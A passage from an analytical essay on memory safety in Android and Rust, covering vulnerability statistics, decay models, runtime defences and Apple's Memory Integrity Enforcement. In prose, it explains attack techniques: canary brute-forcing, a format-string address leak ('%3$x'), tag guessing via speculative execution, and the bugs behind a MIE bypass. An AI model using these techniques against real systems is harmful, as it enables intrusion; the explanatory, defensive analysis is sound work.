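| Year | Memory errors | Share of all vulnerabilities | Others (implied) |
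|---|---|---|---|
| 2019 | 223 | 76% | about 70 |
| 2022 | 85 | 36% | about 150 |
| 2024 | 36 (projected) | 24% | about 115 |
| 2025 | no figure | below 20% | no figure |

The 2024 count is a projection from 27 cases by September. The Hacker News (2025) later put the full-year total at fewer than 50. *Rust in Android*, a Google post from November 2025 (Vander Stoep, 2025), gives the 2025 share, which fell below a fifth for the first time.

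The drop in share slightly exaggerates the improvement, because other vulnerabilities became more common. If those had stayed at about 70 a year, memory errors would have made up about a third of the total in 2024. But the number of memory errors also fell by 84 percent in five years, and they tended to be the most serious vulnerabilities. In 2022 they made up 36 percent of the vulnerabilities in the bulletins, but 86 percent of the critical ones and 89 percent of those that an attacker could exploit remotely. Google explains that a flaw in a permission check usually exposes one resource, whereas a memory error can give an attacker everything the program can access.

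Google does not appear to have published a share for 2026, and the year's bulletins are hard to compare with earlier ones. Since July 2025, according to heise's *Patchday Android*, Google has fixed only the most dangerous flaws every month and left the rest for quarterly updates, so the totals vary widely. CyberScoop reported 129 fixes in March, then the most in a month since 2018. Arghire (2026), in *Android's October 2026 Updates Patch 25 Vulnerabilities*, reported 25 in October, and The Hacker News' *Google Issues Patches for Critical Android Flaw That Could Allow RCE* (2026) reported 216 in November. The most prominent flaw in November was a buffer overflow in a C++ file.

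If memory errors made up a fifth of November's total, there would have been 43 that month, more than Google projected for all of 2024. The number of memory errors could therefore be rising again even if their share is not. This isn't evidence of a reversal, though, because the bulletins also cover chipmakers' components, which Google's own counts may leave out.

### Why the old code could stay

In 2024 most of Android's code was still in memory-unsafe languages. Google attributes the decline in memory safety vulnerabilities to the age of that code. Vulnerabilities are concentrated in new or recently changed code, because people gradually find and fix the ones in older code.

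Suppose that people find the same fraction of the remaining vulnerabilities every year, however long those have been there. Their lifetimes then follow an exponential distribution. If the mean lifetime is λ years, and nobody adds new errors to a piece of code, its density of vulnerabilities after t years is

```
density(t) = density(0) × e^(−t/λ)
```

Google uses a mean lifetime of 2.5 years, based on its experience with Android and with Chromium, the code behind the Chrome browser. After five years the exponent is −2, so five-year-old code has e^−2, or about 13.5%, as many vulnerabilities per line as new code. Rewriting a five-year-old component in Rust would therefore remove less than a seventh as many vulnerabilities as writing a new component of the same size in Rust would prevent. A team that can't do both should start with the new component.

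The same arithmetic explains why finding and fixing bugs never seemed to reduce their number much. If a system has 1,000 undiscovered memory errors with a mean lifetime of 2.5 years, people initially find them at a rate of 400 a year. If programmers also add 400 a year, the total stays at 1,000. If they stop adding any, 670 remain after one year and 135 after five. If they only halve the number they add, the total falls towards 500, reaching about 570 after five years.

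Google simulated a more realistic case, in which the whole code base doubles every six years. New code moves to memory-safe languages over ten years, slowly at first, then faster, then slowly again. Programmers change old code only to fix bugs. By the end, there is more unsafe code than at the start, but there are far fewer memory errors, because most of the unsafe code is old.

The simulation shows that the policy can work if its assumptions hold, but it is not evidence that they do. The most important assumption is the exponential decay.

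### How long vulnerabilities survive

Alexopoulos, Brack and colleagues (2022), in *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?*, collected 5,914 vulnerabilities from 11 open-source projects, mostly written in C or C++, for which they could identify the change that fixed the problem. The change that caused a vulnerability is harder to find, so they estimated its date by taking a weighted average of the dates when programmers had last edited the lines touched by the fix. On 1,171 vulnerabilities whose origin was known, this method overestimated the average lifetime by 117 days. It was often wrong by years for a single vulnerability, so they used it only for averages over at least 20 vulnerabilities.

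The mean lifetime of vulnerabilities was 1,501 days, or about four years, and an exponential curve fitted all but the longest-lived 2 percent well. With that mean, five-year-old code has 3.4 times fewer vulnerabilities than new code. The mean varied a lot between projects. It was 758 days for Chromium and 3,169 for tcpdump, a tool that records network traffic. Within the three largest projects, though, memory errors lasted about as long as other vulnerabilities, so it seems reasonable to apply the general curve to them.

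Alexopoulos and colleagues also found that the average age of fixed vulnerabilities was rising by about 43 days a year. If this was because programmers were adding fewer new ones, leaving old ones to make up more of the total, the distribution of ages should have changed shape, but it stayed exponential. They concluded that programmers were probably adding vulnerabilities as fast as before. This supports Google's claim that better testing of C and C++ had not solved the problem.

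A larger data set fits an exponential distribution less well. Qu (2026), in *Kernel bugs hide for 2 years on average. Some hide for 20*, traced 125,183 Linux kernel bugs using developers' notes that link a fix to the earlier change it repairs. The bugs are of all kinds, and few are catalogued as vulnerabilities. Their mean lifetime was 2.1 years and their median was 0.7 years. An exponential distribution with that mean would have a median of about 1.5 years, and fewer than 1 percent of bugs would last ten years, but 4.2 percent of the bugs in Qu's data did. Qu points out that recent bugs have not had time to reach that age, so the true proportion is probably higher.

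The decay therefore seems to slow down, because people find the easy bugs within months and the rest can stay for a very long time. Of Qu's bugs, 13.5 percent lasted more than five years, which matches Google's formula. At ten years, more than twice as many remain as the formula predicts.

Neither data set includes bugs that nobody has found, and this is a bigger gap than it used to be. Schneier (2026), in *LLMs are Getting a Lot Better and Faster at Finding and Exploiting*, quotes Anthropic's account that its model Claude Opus 4.6 found serious vulnerabilities, some of them decades old, in projects that had gone through years of fuzzing (automated testing that feeds a program huge numbers of odd inputs). If AI makes such flaws easy to find, attackers can find them too, and leaving old C++ in place is riskier than the decay curve suggests. New code would probably still come first, but the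 case for rewriting some old code is stronger than it was in 2024.

### Other reasons for Android's decline

Android's own record is close to what the decay model predicts. If nobody had added memory errors to Android after 2019, a mean lifetime of 2.5 years would have brought the annual count down from 223 to about 67 in 2022 and 30 in 2024. The actual count was 85 in 2022, and the projected count for 2024 was 36.

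But the team kept adding C++. According to Google, only 21 percent of the new native code (C, C++ and Rust) in Android 13, the 2022 release, was in Rust. Vander Stoep reports that in the part of Android that Google writes itself, Rust didn't grow about as much as C++ until 2024. If the team had immediately halved the number of new memory errors in 2019, the model would give about 127 cases in 2024, three and a half times the projected number.

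So the switch to safe languages probably did not cause the whole decline, unless the remaining C++ also became much safer. Over the same years, Google hardened Android's memory allocator, put error detectors on phones in use and did more fuzzing, which may explain some of the rest. Google acknowledges that the results were better than its simulation and suggests its work on unsafe code as a possible reason. It's also possible that 2019 was an unusually bad year, or that bug hunters later turned to other kinds of flaw, which would fit the rise in other vulnerabilities. *Don't Judge an AI-Discovered CVE by Its Category*, an analysis by the security company Securin, illustrates how much the kinds of flaw found depend on who is searching. In it, memory corruption accounts for 50.1 percent of the weaknesses that AI tools discovered, but only 18.4 percent of all those catalogued in 2026.

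An experiment could separate these causes by comparing two similar versions of Android with the same testing and defences, only one of which allowed safe languages, but nobody has run anything like that. The nearest substitute is Google's observation that other projects adopted the same detection tools without a similar shift in their vulnerabilities. This suggests the tools weren't the sole explanation, but Google doesn't name the projects, and they may have differed from Android in other ways.

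Google also has an interest in the result, since it chose the policy and has promoted it to the industry. Outsiders can check the number of flaws in the bulletins, but they can't easily check how Google classified each one or which code it counted as new. Safe languages are very likely a major cause of the decline, as Google believes, but the trend alone can't show how much they contributed.

### One near-miss in five million lines

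Vander Stoep reports that Android contained about 5 million lines of Rust in 2025 and that the team had found one potential memory vulnerability in them, which it fixed before release. That is 0.2 per million lines, compared with Google's historical figure of about 1,000 per million for C and C++. The C and C++ rate is about 5,000 times the Rust rate, though Google cautiously reports the difference as "more than 1000x".

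One event is very little data. If errors turn up independently, the Poisson distribution gives the probability of seeing any particular number of them. Suppose the true density were high enough that one would expect 5.57 errors in 5 million lines. The chance of finding at most one would then be

```
e^(−5.57) × (1 + 5.57) = 0.025
```

At the other extreme, if the expected number of errors were only 0.025, the chance of finding at least one would also be about 2.5 percent. The 95 percent confidence interval therefore runs from 0.025 to 5.57 errors, or 0.005 to 1.1 per million lines. Even at the top of that range, Rust's error density would be about 900 times lower than the figure for C and C++.

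A month after Vander Stoep's post, a second case appeared. Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Rust Code Sees Its First CVE Vulnerability* describes an error that can corrupt memory in the unsafe Rust code of a driver that Android programs use to communicate with each other. It is unclear whether the driver was part of the 5 million lines. If it was, the low end of the ratio's range drops from about 900 to about 700.

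The age of the code is a bigger problem for the comparison than chance. Android had 1.5 million lines of Rust at the end of 2022, so most of the 5 million lines it had in 2025 were less than three years old. If the code grew steadily between those dates, and Rust errors take as long to surface as other Android errors, people would have found only about half of the eventual total by 2025. Using the four-year mean from Alexopoulos and colleagues, they would have found about 40 percent. The code's age could therefore account for a factor of 2 or 2.5 in the comparison.

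The figure for C and C++ is also doubtful as an average. In 2022 Google described it as typical of "many" components and named media, Bluetooth and NFC (the short-range radio used for payments). These handle complicated data from untrusted sources, so they are likely to have more vulnerabilities than other components.

A rough check suggests that the usual figure for Android's C++, 1,000 vulnerabilities per million lines, is too high by a factor of about five. An undated page from the Android Open Source Project puts memory-unsafe languages at over 70 percent of the platform's code. If that was still true when Android had 5 million lines of Rust, it also had at least 12 million lines of C and C++. At the usual figure, those lines would have contained about 12,000 vulnerabilities. Reporting them all at the 2019 rate of 223 a year would take more than fifty years, and Android is less than twenty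 years old. Ten years at that rate would come to about 190 per million lines. This correction is imprecise because the bulletins leave out minor flaws.

Nobody has published a measure of how hard people have searched Android's Rust code for vulnerabilities. Security researchers have attacked Android's media and Bluetooth code for years, and some may avoid Rust because they expect to find little. But Google also used Rust for difficult jobs, such as storing cryptographic keys, implementing a new radio protocol and running virtual machines.

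Correcting the ratio of 5,000 for the Rust code's youth and for the C++ average reduces it to around 500. If we also guess that people searched the Rust code only a tenth as hard as the C++ code, it falls to about 50. Starting from 900 and making the correction least favourable to Rust at every step still leaves Rust ahead by a factor of 7. It seems safer to conclude that the advantage is in the tens or hundreds than that it is "more than 1000x". That is still a very large advantage, and it is much harder to attribute to other defences than the decline in the annual counts is, since many of those defences help find errors in both kinds of code.

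About 4 percent of Android's Rust code, or around 200,000 lines, is inside `unsafe` blocks. If those lines were as faulty as C++, they would contain 200 vulnerabilities at Google's figure for C++ vulnerability density, or about 38 at the lower figure, but the team had found only one. Vander Stoep isn't sure why, but suggests that most of Rust's checks still apply inside these blocks, that programmers can reason about each small block separately, and that reviewers look at them more carefully. The code for the new radio protocol had only two uses of `unsafe`, and the extra attention they received led the team to a possible timing error.

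### Rollbacks and code review

Vander Stoep reports that Rust sped up development in Android, whereas safety measures usually slow down programmers or the product. The data come from changes made by Google's own developers. For medium and large changes, Rust's rate of rollbacks (emergency removals of changes that have caused trouble) was about a quarter of C++'s. Rust changes also needed about 20 percent fewer revisions than C++ changes of similar size and spent about 25 percent less time in review.

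Google tried to make the comparison fair by grouping the changes by size and leaving out outside contributors. Many of the developers also worked in both languages. But Google did not assign the work at random. A team that starts a new component in Rust can choose a clean design, while a programmer who changes C++ may have to work around decisions made ten years earlier. Developers who choose Rust may also be more careful or more experienced. The published charts show no units for the rollback rates, so a fourfold difference could mean 4 percent against 1 percent, or 0.4 percent against 0.1 percent.

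Even if these differences come partly from the kind of work, they weaken the common objection that safe languages make development too slow. Rust's advantage in review times also grew considerably between 2023 and 2024, which suggests that learning the language slowed the team only temporarily. Vander Stoep guesses that the growth came from the team's increasing experience.

Some of the savings come from removing other defences. Google cites a component in Chromium that draws QR codes. Developers had to run it in a sandbox, a closed-off process that limits the damage from an attack. After they wrote it in Rust, they no longer needed the sandbox, and the component became 20 times faster.

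### Typed interfaces against cross-site scripting

Cross-site scripting is a web vulnerability that resembles the memory errors in C. A web page combines content to display and instructions for the browser in a single stream of text, much as a language model's prompt mixes the developer's instructions with the user's words. If a website inserts a visitor's comment into a page unchanged, and the comment contains a script, the browsers of everyone who reads the comment will run the script. Attackers use this to take over other people's accounts.

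The usual defence is to escape the comment by replacing characters such as `<` with codes that browsers display as text instead of interpreting as HTML. This works wherever programmers remember to do it, but a large site inserts text in thousands of places, and an attacker can exploit a single omission.

Google changed the function that inserts content into a page so that it accepts only values of a special type, not ordinary strings. Programmers can obtain these values only from a small library that escapes text or builds pages from fixed templates. If they forget to escape a comment, the types don't match and the program does not compile. The trusted base consists of the library and the exceptions needed for content it can't handle, which experts review as they review `unsafe` blocks in Rust.

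This approach prevents cross-site scripting, a hazard unrelated to memory, by construction and without a new programming language. Google credits it with "remarkable success" in eliminating the problem but gives no numbers for this in its account of memory safety. The case is therefore good evidence that the design can be used elsewhere, but weaker evidence of how well it works.

### Microsoft, Chromium and the Linux kernel

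Other organisations have published more about how common memory errors are than about the effect of changing languages. Microsoft has attributed about 70 percent of the vulnerabilities it counted to memory errors, and the Chromium project has attributed about 70 percent of its serious vulnerabilities to them. Google treats 70 percent as the industry norm. Android's share was 76 percent in 2019, so it was a fairly typical product when it started moving new code to memory-safe languages.

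The 70 percent norm applies to large products written mainly in C and C++. Most software does not fit that description, which is why memory corruption makes up only 18.4 percent of the weaknesses Securin counted for 2026. Android's share, at below 20 percent, is therefore low for an operating system but not for software in general. The 70 percent figures also date from around 2020, and a company's share can change for reasons other than its choice of language.

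Chromium has since replaced its parsers for PNG images, web fonts and JSON (a common data format) with versions in Rust. Parsers are a sensible place to begin because they read whatever a website sends them. Vander Stoep lists the replacements but gives no vulnerability counts from before and after. Those counts would have been a useful test on a second product.

The Linux kernel's first catalogued vulnerability in Rust code was the error in the Android driver. Greg Kroah-Hartman, a longtime kernel developer posting as gregkh (2025), noted that the kernel team catalogued 159 vulnerabilities in C code on the same day. That comparison doesn't by itself support his expectation that Rust will eliminate large numbers of kernel vulnerabilities as its use grows, because Rust is still a very small part of the kernel. If Rust made up less than 1 line in 160, it had more than its share of that day's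 vulnerabilities. Drawing conclusions from such counts would require the number of lines in each language, their age and several years of reports, and so far only Google has published even part of that.

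## Tests of runtime defences for memory-unsafe code

Writing new code in Rust does not remove the errors in C and C++ code already in use. Those errors remain until someone finds and fixes them, and runtime defences protect the code in the meantime.

When Szekeres and colleagues surveyed these defences in 2013, memory attacks had been a problem for more than 30 years. They divided an attack into steps. The attacker makes a pointer invalid, uses it to read or write memory, changes something valuable such as a return address, supplies a useful new value, and gets the program to act on it. Each defence blocks one step, so an attacker who gets around that step can continue. Canaries, non-executable memory and address randomisation were already in common use, and real attacks had defeated all of them. Hackers broke into Google's Chrome browser four times at contests in 2012. Researchers had proposed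 many stricter defences, but most went unused because they slowed programs too much, did not work with existing code or had gaps of their own.

Some defences depend on keeping a value secret from the attacker, while others apply a fixed rule that works equally well if the attacker knows it.

| Defence | What it does | What gets past it | Basis |
|---|---|---|---|
| Stack canary | Checks a value beside the return address before a function returns | Writes that skip the canary; errors outside the stack | Secret |
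| Address randomisation | Moves code and data to unpredictable places | Any error, once the attacker learns an address | Secret |
| Memory tagging | Compares the pointer's tag with the memory's tag | Errors inside one object; chance matches | Secret and chance, except between neighbours |
| Non-executable memory | Stops the processor from running data as code | Reuse of the program's own code; changes to data | Fixed rule |
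| Control-flow integrity | Checks where a jump or return leads | Changes to data; wrong but permitted jumps | Usually a fixed rule |
| Typed allocator | Keeps different types of object apart | Errors among objects of the same type | Mostly a fixed rule |
| Bounds-checked C++ library | Checks each index into the library's lists | Plain pointers; use after free | Fixed rule |
| Sandbox | Restricts what a process can reach | Damage inside the sandbox; operating system flaws | Fixed rule |
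| CHERI | Checks each access against limits stored in the pointer | Crashes; errors in the program's logic | Fixed rule |

### Canaries and randomised addresses

A stack canary adds one write and one comparison to each function call. Huang, Payer and colleagues (2024), in *Comprehensive Memory Safety Validation*, observe that developers have adopted incomplete defences with low overhead, like this one, and found the overhead of more complete ones too high. A canary doesn't detect an overflow that stops before reaching it, such as one that changes a nearby variable recording whether the user is an administrator.

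The number of guesses an attacker gets also matters. Some servers handle each connection in a fresh copy of one process, and every copy has the same canary. An attacker can overwrite only the canary's first byte and try its 256 possible values. A wrong guess crashes only one copy, so the attacker can keep guessing until a copy doesn't crash, then move on to the next byte. An eight-byte canary takes at most 8 × 256 = 2,048 guesses this way, although it has 2^64 possible values.

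Address randomisation performs no checks while the program runs, so it slows the program very little, but an attacker can defeat it if the program leaks an address. Szekeres and colleagues give the example of a program that passes a user's text to C's `printf` function as a formatting instruction. A user who types `%3$x` gets back a number from the program's memory, which may be an address. One address is often enough, because randomisation usually moves a whole library as a block and leaves the distances inside it unchanged.

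Huang and colleagues use randomisation in a way that such leaks don't defeat. Their tools look for objects that no pointer can misuse, then move them to a separate, hidden region. The rest of memory contains no pointers to that region, so a leak from the rest of memory can't reveal the region's location. In 1,245 Ubuntu Linux packages, the tools proved that 85 percent of the objects on the stack were safe from pointer misuse. For the heap, which is the memory that programs reserve as they run, the tools proved bounds and type safety at 78 percent of the places where programs create objects, and a special allocator handled memory reuse. On average, the stack protection slowed programs by 4.3 percent and the heap protection by 2.9 percent.

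Slowdowns like these depend heavily on the implementation. SafeStack's inventors had reported a slowdown of 0.1 percent for their earlier stack-separating method, but Huang and colleagues measured 11.3 percent for the version in Clang, a widely used compiler.

### Guessing one tag in sixteen

Suppose an allocator gives every object one of 16 tags at random, and an attacker has a bug that writes to some distant object. The pointer's tag matches the object's tag with probability 1/16, or 6.25 percent. Otherwise the program crashes. If it restarts with new tags and the attacker can try again, the chance of at least one success in k tries is

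```
1 − (15/16)^k
```

The chance of at least one tag match passes 50 percent at 11 tries and 95 percent at 47. An attack that needs three independent matches in a row works once in 4,096 tries on average, but it works every time if the attacker can learn the tags first.

The value of tagging therefore depends on who is attacking. A criminal who sends the attack once to each of 1,000 phones takes over about 62 of them, which may be enough. A spy who wants one particular person's phone will probably fail on the first try. Each failed attempt causes a crash, which may leave a log that leads the manufacturer to the bug, and the criminal's attack causes more than 900 such crashes.

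Attackers can learn tags through speculative execution, in which a processor saves time by running instructions before it knows whether the program will need them. The processor discards any results the program doesn't need, but the discarded work can still affect how long later operations take. An attacker can use these timing differences to test guesses at a tag without a wrong guess causing a crash. Apple, a competitor of Google, cites two attacks published by other researchers, TikTag and StickyTags, that do this on Google's Pixel phones.

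Apple also found two weaknesses in Arm's original tagging design. In one mode, the processor reported a mismatch only after the access, which gave an attacker a moment to act. The hardware did not check accesses to untagged memory, such as a program's global variables. Apple worked with Arm on a revised design and rejected the delayed mode for its own devices.

### Defences that need no secret

Nearly all modern processors support non-executable memory, which adds almost no overhead. Browsers need an exception because they translate a page's JavaScript into machine code while the page is open and then run it. Non-executable memory also doesn't stop return-oriented programming, which uses code that the processor is allowed to run.

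Control-flow integrity restricts that reuse by making a program check that an address read from memory is a permitted destination before jumping to it. Since 2018, Apple's chips have similarly used a secret to add a cryptographic signature to a pointer, and they check the signature before using the pointer. In the first version, an attacker could work out a valid signature from timing differences exposed by speculative execution. Neither method stops an attacker who changes only data, such as the administrator variable.

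A typed allocator makes a use-after-free bug less useful to an attacker. If only objects of the same type can reuse a freed object's memory, the attacker can't put text where the program expects a function's address. Apple reports that its allocators run at least as fast as the ones they replaced. But they separate memory in 16-kilobyte pages, so they can't keep small objects of similar types apart. A hardened allocator also neutralised the near-miss in Android's Rust code.

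Bounds checks now slow programs much less than the 2013 survey might suggest. The lists in C++'s standard library record their length, unlike plain C arrays, so a check needs only one comparison. Google's *Retrofitting spatial safety to hundreds of millions of lines of C++* (2024) describes how the company switched these checks on because out-of-bounds errors accounted for 40 percent of the memory-safety exploits that attackers had used in the past decade. The post, by Rebert, Shavrick and Yasuda, reports an average performance overhead of 0.30 percent across Google's services. *Hardening the C++ Standard Library at massive scale*, by Dionne, Rebert and colleagues (2025), also describes the overhead as minimal.

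The change still took more than a year. Google (2024) first ran the checks in its tests, where they exposed hundreds of unknown bugs, and then gave developers time to fix the code before the checks reached users. Even a third of a percent of overhead required a lot of computing power at Google's scale.

The compiler builds these checks into the program, as it does in Rust, so they are an intrinsic control. They protect less than Rust's checks because a C++ programmer can use a plain pointer anywhere without marking the code as unsafe. They also don't catch use-after-free errors.

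A sandbox, which limits the damage from an attack, can slow small jobs down a lot, as it did with Chromium's QR codes. A sandbox also depends on the operating system's kernel, the core that controls access to everything else. Most kernels are written largely in C, and a memory error in the kernel can let an attacker out of the sandbox.

CHERI, a processor design, comes close to a complete monitor for C. It replaces ordinary pointers with capabilities, which store an object's bounds and what the program may do with it. Every memory access needs a capability, and a program can reduce a capability's permissions but never increase them. If a program tries to write to cell 100 of an array with cells 0 to 99, the processor blocks the write. It checks the address against the stored bounds, so an attacker can't get past the check by guessing a tag.

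*CHERI Myths*, an essay by a developer of CHERIoT, a CHERI system for small devices, says that researchers have formally verified these properties for two versions of the instruction set, but it calls CHERI's guarantee much weaker than that of most safe languages. Rust's compiler makes programmers fix many errors before release, while CHERI stops the program when a user runs into them. Dividing the program into compartments can limit the damage. In CHERIoT, a memory error in the networking code resets only that compartment. But CHERI needs new chips and larger pointers. The essay also gives no measurements of CHERI's speed, and poor speed was a large part of why the stricter defences were not in use in 2013.

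### Attacks on Apple's Memory Integrity Enforcement

Apple combined several of these defences in Memory Integrity Enforcement (MIE), introduced with the iPhone 17. Typed allocators separate groups of objects, and tags separate the small objects within a group. The chip reports every tag mismatch immediately, and tags do not influence speculative execution. Apple gives no figure for the slowdown but says it dedicated an extraordinary amount of chip resources to security.

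Apple's own attack team worked on MIE from 2020 to 2025. The team tried to rebuild attacks that spyware companies had used on iPhones, but could not make any of them work against MIE, even after replacing the old bugs with newer ones. Overflows within a single object could still get through, but Apple considers these extremely rare. This is good evidence that MIE stops the attacks Apple knew about, but weaker evidence about new ones, since the designers and testers worked for the same company.

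In May 2026, Calif, an outside security company, announced the first public kernel exploit to get past MIE on a Mac. The exploit gives an ordinary user account complete control of the computer. The team found the bugs on April 25 and had a working exploit by May 1. Mythos Preview, an AI model from Anthropic, helped find the bugs and develop the exploit, though Calif says that getting past MIE took human expertise. The exploit changes only data, so control-flow integrity does not detect it.

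Blazakis, Dang and Maine (2026), in *Apple MIE Exploitation Challenge*, explain the two bugs, both of which involve a malicious file server:

- The Mac asks the server for the path of a file and keeps a record that begins with the file's number. The server labels its reply as a different kind of answer, a "lease". The Mac then treats its own record as a lease record, which begins with an address. It therefore uses a number that the attacker can influence as a memory address.
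- The Mac reserves a large block of memory without clearing it and requests part of a file. The server reports success but sends nothing. The Mac passes the whole block to the program that wanted the file, including whatever the kernel had left there.

The first bug is a type error, whereas tagging mainly targets overflows and uses after free. In the second, the Mac reads only memory that it has properly reserved, so the tags match. Ordinary Rust code rules out both bugs, since it can't treat one kind of record as another or read memory that it has not filled. Blazakis and colleagues saved the rest of the attack for a later talk. But a pointer includes its tag, so the leaked memory may well have given them both tags and addresses.

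Five days is short for a system that took Apple five years, although the team was expert and needed an account on the Mac to start. Later attacks on iPhones needed less initial access. MacTechNews' *Neuer persistenter, untethered Jailbreak für iOS demonstriert* (2026) describes a jailbreak (an attack that removes Apple's restrictions) by Calif. It begins when someone opens a PDF sent in a message, and it survives a restart, which no jailbreak had done since iOS 9. AI again helped find the flaws, and Apple closed most of them in iOS 27.2. iTnews' *Apple rains on MIE-bypassing iPhone jailbreak parade with iOS update* reports that the attack bypassed MIE. Rechsteiner's *Blockierungsmodus geknackt* (2026) reports that in November Calif took over an iPhone 18 Pro in Lockdown Mode, Apple's strictest setting for people at high risk, and kept control of it after an update to iOS 27.2.

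The long wait for an iOS 26 jailbreak suggests that Apple's hardening works. The first public one took 326 days, according to TechSpot's *A jailbreak for iOS 26 is finally here, 326 days after launch*, and Bada (2026), in *La renaissance du jailbreak*, adds that it works only on a handful of older iPhones. But jailbreaks are a poor measure of security, because fewer people want them now and those who can build one may keep it to themselves, as Calif did. MIE probably still makes most attacks harder, but it did not make them too expensive for a small company with a good AI model.

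### Fuzzing, sanitizers and AI

Developers can also look for the errors and fix them. They usually search by combining fuzzing with sanitizers, which are checks that the compiler adds to test versions of a program. A sanitizer reports a stray write immediately; without one, the damage may go unnoticed until much later. These checks are too slow for most finished products, and they catch an error only if a test input triggers it.

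Google built many of these tools, but people have still found vulnerabilities in extensively fuzzed code. Its teams also need constant pressure to run the tools and fix the bugs they find. Google (2025) reports having around a billion lines of C++, with some ten million pointer declarations. It concludes that fuzzing and sanitizers revealed the size of the problem but were not enough to solve it.

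AI models have an advantage in that they can notice an error by reading the code, without an input that triggers it. Calif says that Mythos Preview found the Mac bugs quickly because they belonged to known types, and that once the model has learned to attack one type of problem, it can handle nearly any example. Blazakis and colleagues count 38 vulnerabilities that the company reported to Apple between March and late July 2026, but don't say how many were memory errors or how many the AI found. Other results from 2026 also suggest that AI models are effective at finding bugs. For example, Claude Opus 4.6 found decades-old flaws in heavily fuzzed projects.

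Even with such AI models, the decay model for Android's vulnerabilities suggests that new languages are still necessary. In the earlier example, a system has 1,000 undiscovered memory errors and gains 400 new ones a year. If AI cuts their average lifetime from 2.5 years to three months, the total falls to 100. But programmers still add 400 a year, and developers have to fix them all and get the updates onto people's devices while attackers search the same code with similar AI models.

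Using AI to check code before release would help more, since it reduces the 400. It would have to catch 98 percent of new memory errors to match a language with a 50-fold advantage over C++, and 99.8 percent to match one with a 500-fold advantage. A count of bugs found, such as Calif's 38, can't show what share the search missed.

AI weakens the argument that nobody can find the memory errors in old code fast enough, but it also makes the remaining errors more dangerous. A compiler that rejects these errors is still the safer choice for new code. AI's effect on the safety of old code depends on whether defenders or attackers find the errors first, which may differ between a company with a large security team and a volunteer project.

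### Four generations of defence

Google divides the history of memory safety into four generations. In the first, companies fixed vulnerabilities after someone had reported or exploited them, which left users exposed. The second added defences such as canaries and control-flow integrity. Google objects that these slow programs down, drain batteries and use memory, while attackers keep finding ways around them. The third was fuzzing and sanitizers, which in Google's view treat the symptoms. The fourth is prevention, through safe languages and interfaces that make the errors impossible to write.

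Google's best argument for prevention is that a developer who compiles a program in ordinary Rust can name errors it does not contain, provided that the trusted base is sound. After a year of fuzzing, the developer could say only how much the program had been tested.

Google's own practice is less tidy than the four generations suggest. Two months after publishing this account, the company described its bounds checks for C++, which apply part of the fourth generation to old code. In a position paper, Google argues that only safe languages can give high assurance, but acknowledges that hundreds of millions of lines of C++ are in active use. It also expects older methods to remain useful. It plans to use runtime defences more selectively, and expects fuzzing to work better on small, isolated pieces of unsafe code.

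The argument for runtime defences is that they protect existing code immediately. CHERIoT's essay estimates that open-source projects alone contain about ten billion lines of C and C++, and that rewriting them would cost at least hundreds of billions of dollars. AI models that write code could lower that cost considerably. But a rewrite can introduce other kinds of errors, and some code, such as a memory allocator, can never be entirely safe.

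For a rough comparison over time, suppose that 40 percent of the 1,000 undiscovered memory errors in the same system are out-of-bounds errors, the same share as among real exploits. If bounds checks covered all of these (C++ library checks cover fewer), they would turn 400 exploitable errors into crashes on the day of release. A company that instead stopped writing unsafe code would need about 15 months to reduce the total by 400. After five years, though, the company that only added bounds checks would still have 600 exploitable errors, because its programmers would keep adding new ones. The company that only stopped writing unsafe code would have 135, and a company that did both would have 81.

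## Failures reported in memory-safe code

Rust code has far fewer memory errors per line than C++, but still has some. Ordinary Rust is memory-safe only if its trusted base is correct, which includes the program's unsafe code, the standard library and the compiler. In 2025 and 2026, people reported memory errors in all three. Memory-safe programs have also failed badly without any memory error.

### An overflow in an image library

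Google counted one potential memory vulnerability in Android's five million lines of Rust. It was in CrabbyAVIF, a library that decodes AVIF images. The library's unsafe code could write past the end of a buffer into the memory immediately after it, which Vander Stoep calls a linear buffer overflow.

Luck and Scudo, Android's default memory allocator, limited the damage. Scudo gives each large object its own block of memory between two guard pages, which are ranges of addresses that the program may not access. The overflow moved steadily forward, so it always hit a guard page before reaching another object, and the processor stopped the program. An attacker could have used the bug only to cause a crash.

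The crash also exposed the bug, which might otherwise have corrupted memory silently. But the crash reports did not make clear that an overflow was the cause, so the team took longer to respond. Google has since changed the reports to identify such overflows. The team fixed the bug before release but still listed it in the public Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE) catalogue, as CVE-2025-48530, to make sure the fix got priority.

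In this case a bolt-on defence contained a failure of prevention by construction, but it might not contain the next one. Scudo does not put guard pages between small objects, and a write that lands far beyond its buffer can skip over a guard page. Some Android devices don't use Scudo, although Google is trying to make it mandatory. A manufacturer that dropped Scudo because of Rust would lose the protection that worked here.

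### A wrong comment in the Linux kernel

The first catalogued vulnerability in the Linux kernel's Rust code, CVE-2025-68260, came from a mistaken assumption that a programmer had written in a comment. The code is in Binder, the driver that Android programs use to communicate with each other. As Red Hat's *CVE-2025-68260 kernel* (2025) explains, the driver keeps a list in which each item has pointers to the items before and after it. A thread has to change these pointers to remove an item. Two threads that change the same pointers at once can corrupt the list, so threads normally take a lock first.

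Removing an item is an unsafe operation, because the compiler can't confirm that no other thread is using the item's pointers. The comment argued that the removal was safe because an item is always either in this list or in no list. Another function in the driver broke that rule:

1. It took the lock.
2. It moved all the items to a temporary list.
3. It released the lock.
4. It worked through the temporary list.

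During step 4, the items are in a list that the comment doesn't cover, and the lock no longer protects them. If another thread removes one of them at that moment, both threads change the same pointers.

The developers fixed the bug by changing this function to take items directly off the original list. They could leave the unsafe line unchanged because it was correct as long as the rest of the driver followed the rule. Someone who reviewed only that line would have had trouble finding the mistake. The trusted base therefore includes both the lines inside `unsafe` blocks and any ordinary code that can break a rule those lines depend on. Rust programmers usually limit the amount of such code by keeping the data those rules cover private to a small module. A formal proof, like the one Jung and colleagues gave for Rust's locks, would have had to account for the temporary list, whereas the compiler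 ignores rules written in comments.

gregkh describes the result as a crash that gives an attacker no way to exploit the corrupted memory. The crash log that Red Hat reproduces is consistent with this, although a log of one crash can't rule out a cleverer attack.

### Errors in Rust's standard library

Nearly every Rust program uses the standard library, so its bugs can affect software well beyond the devices that use the Binder driver. *Verifying the Rust Standard Library* counts about 7,500 unsafe functions in the library and 3,000 safe functions that use unsafe code. Developers reported more than 74 soundness bugs in the library in three years. A soundness bug lets code without the `unsafe` label cause undefined behaviour, which means Rust no longer guarantees anything about what the program will do.

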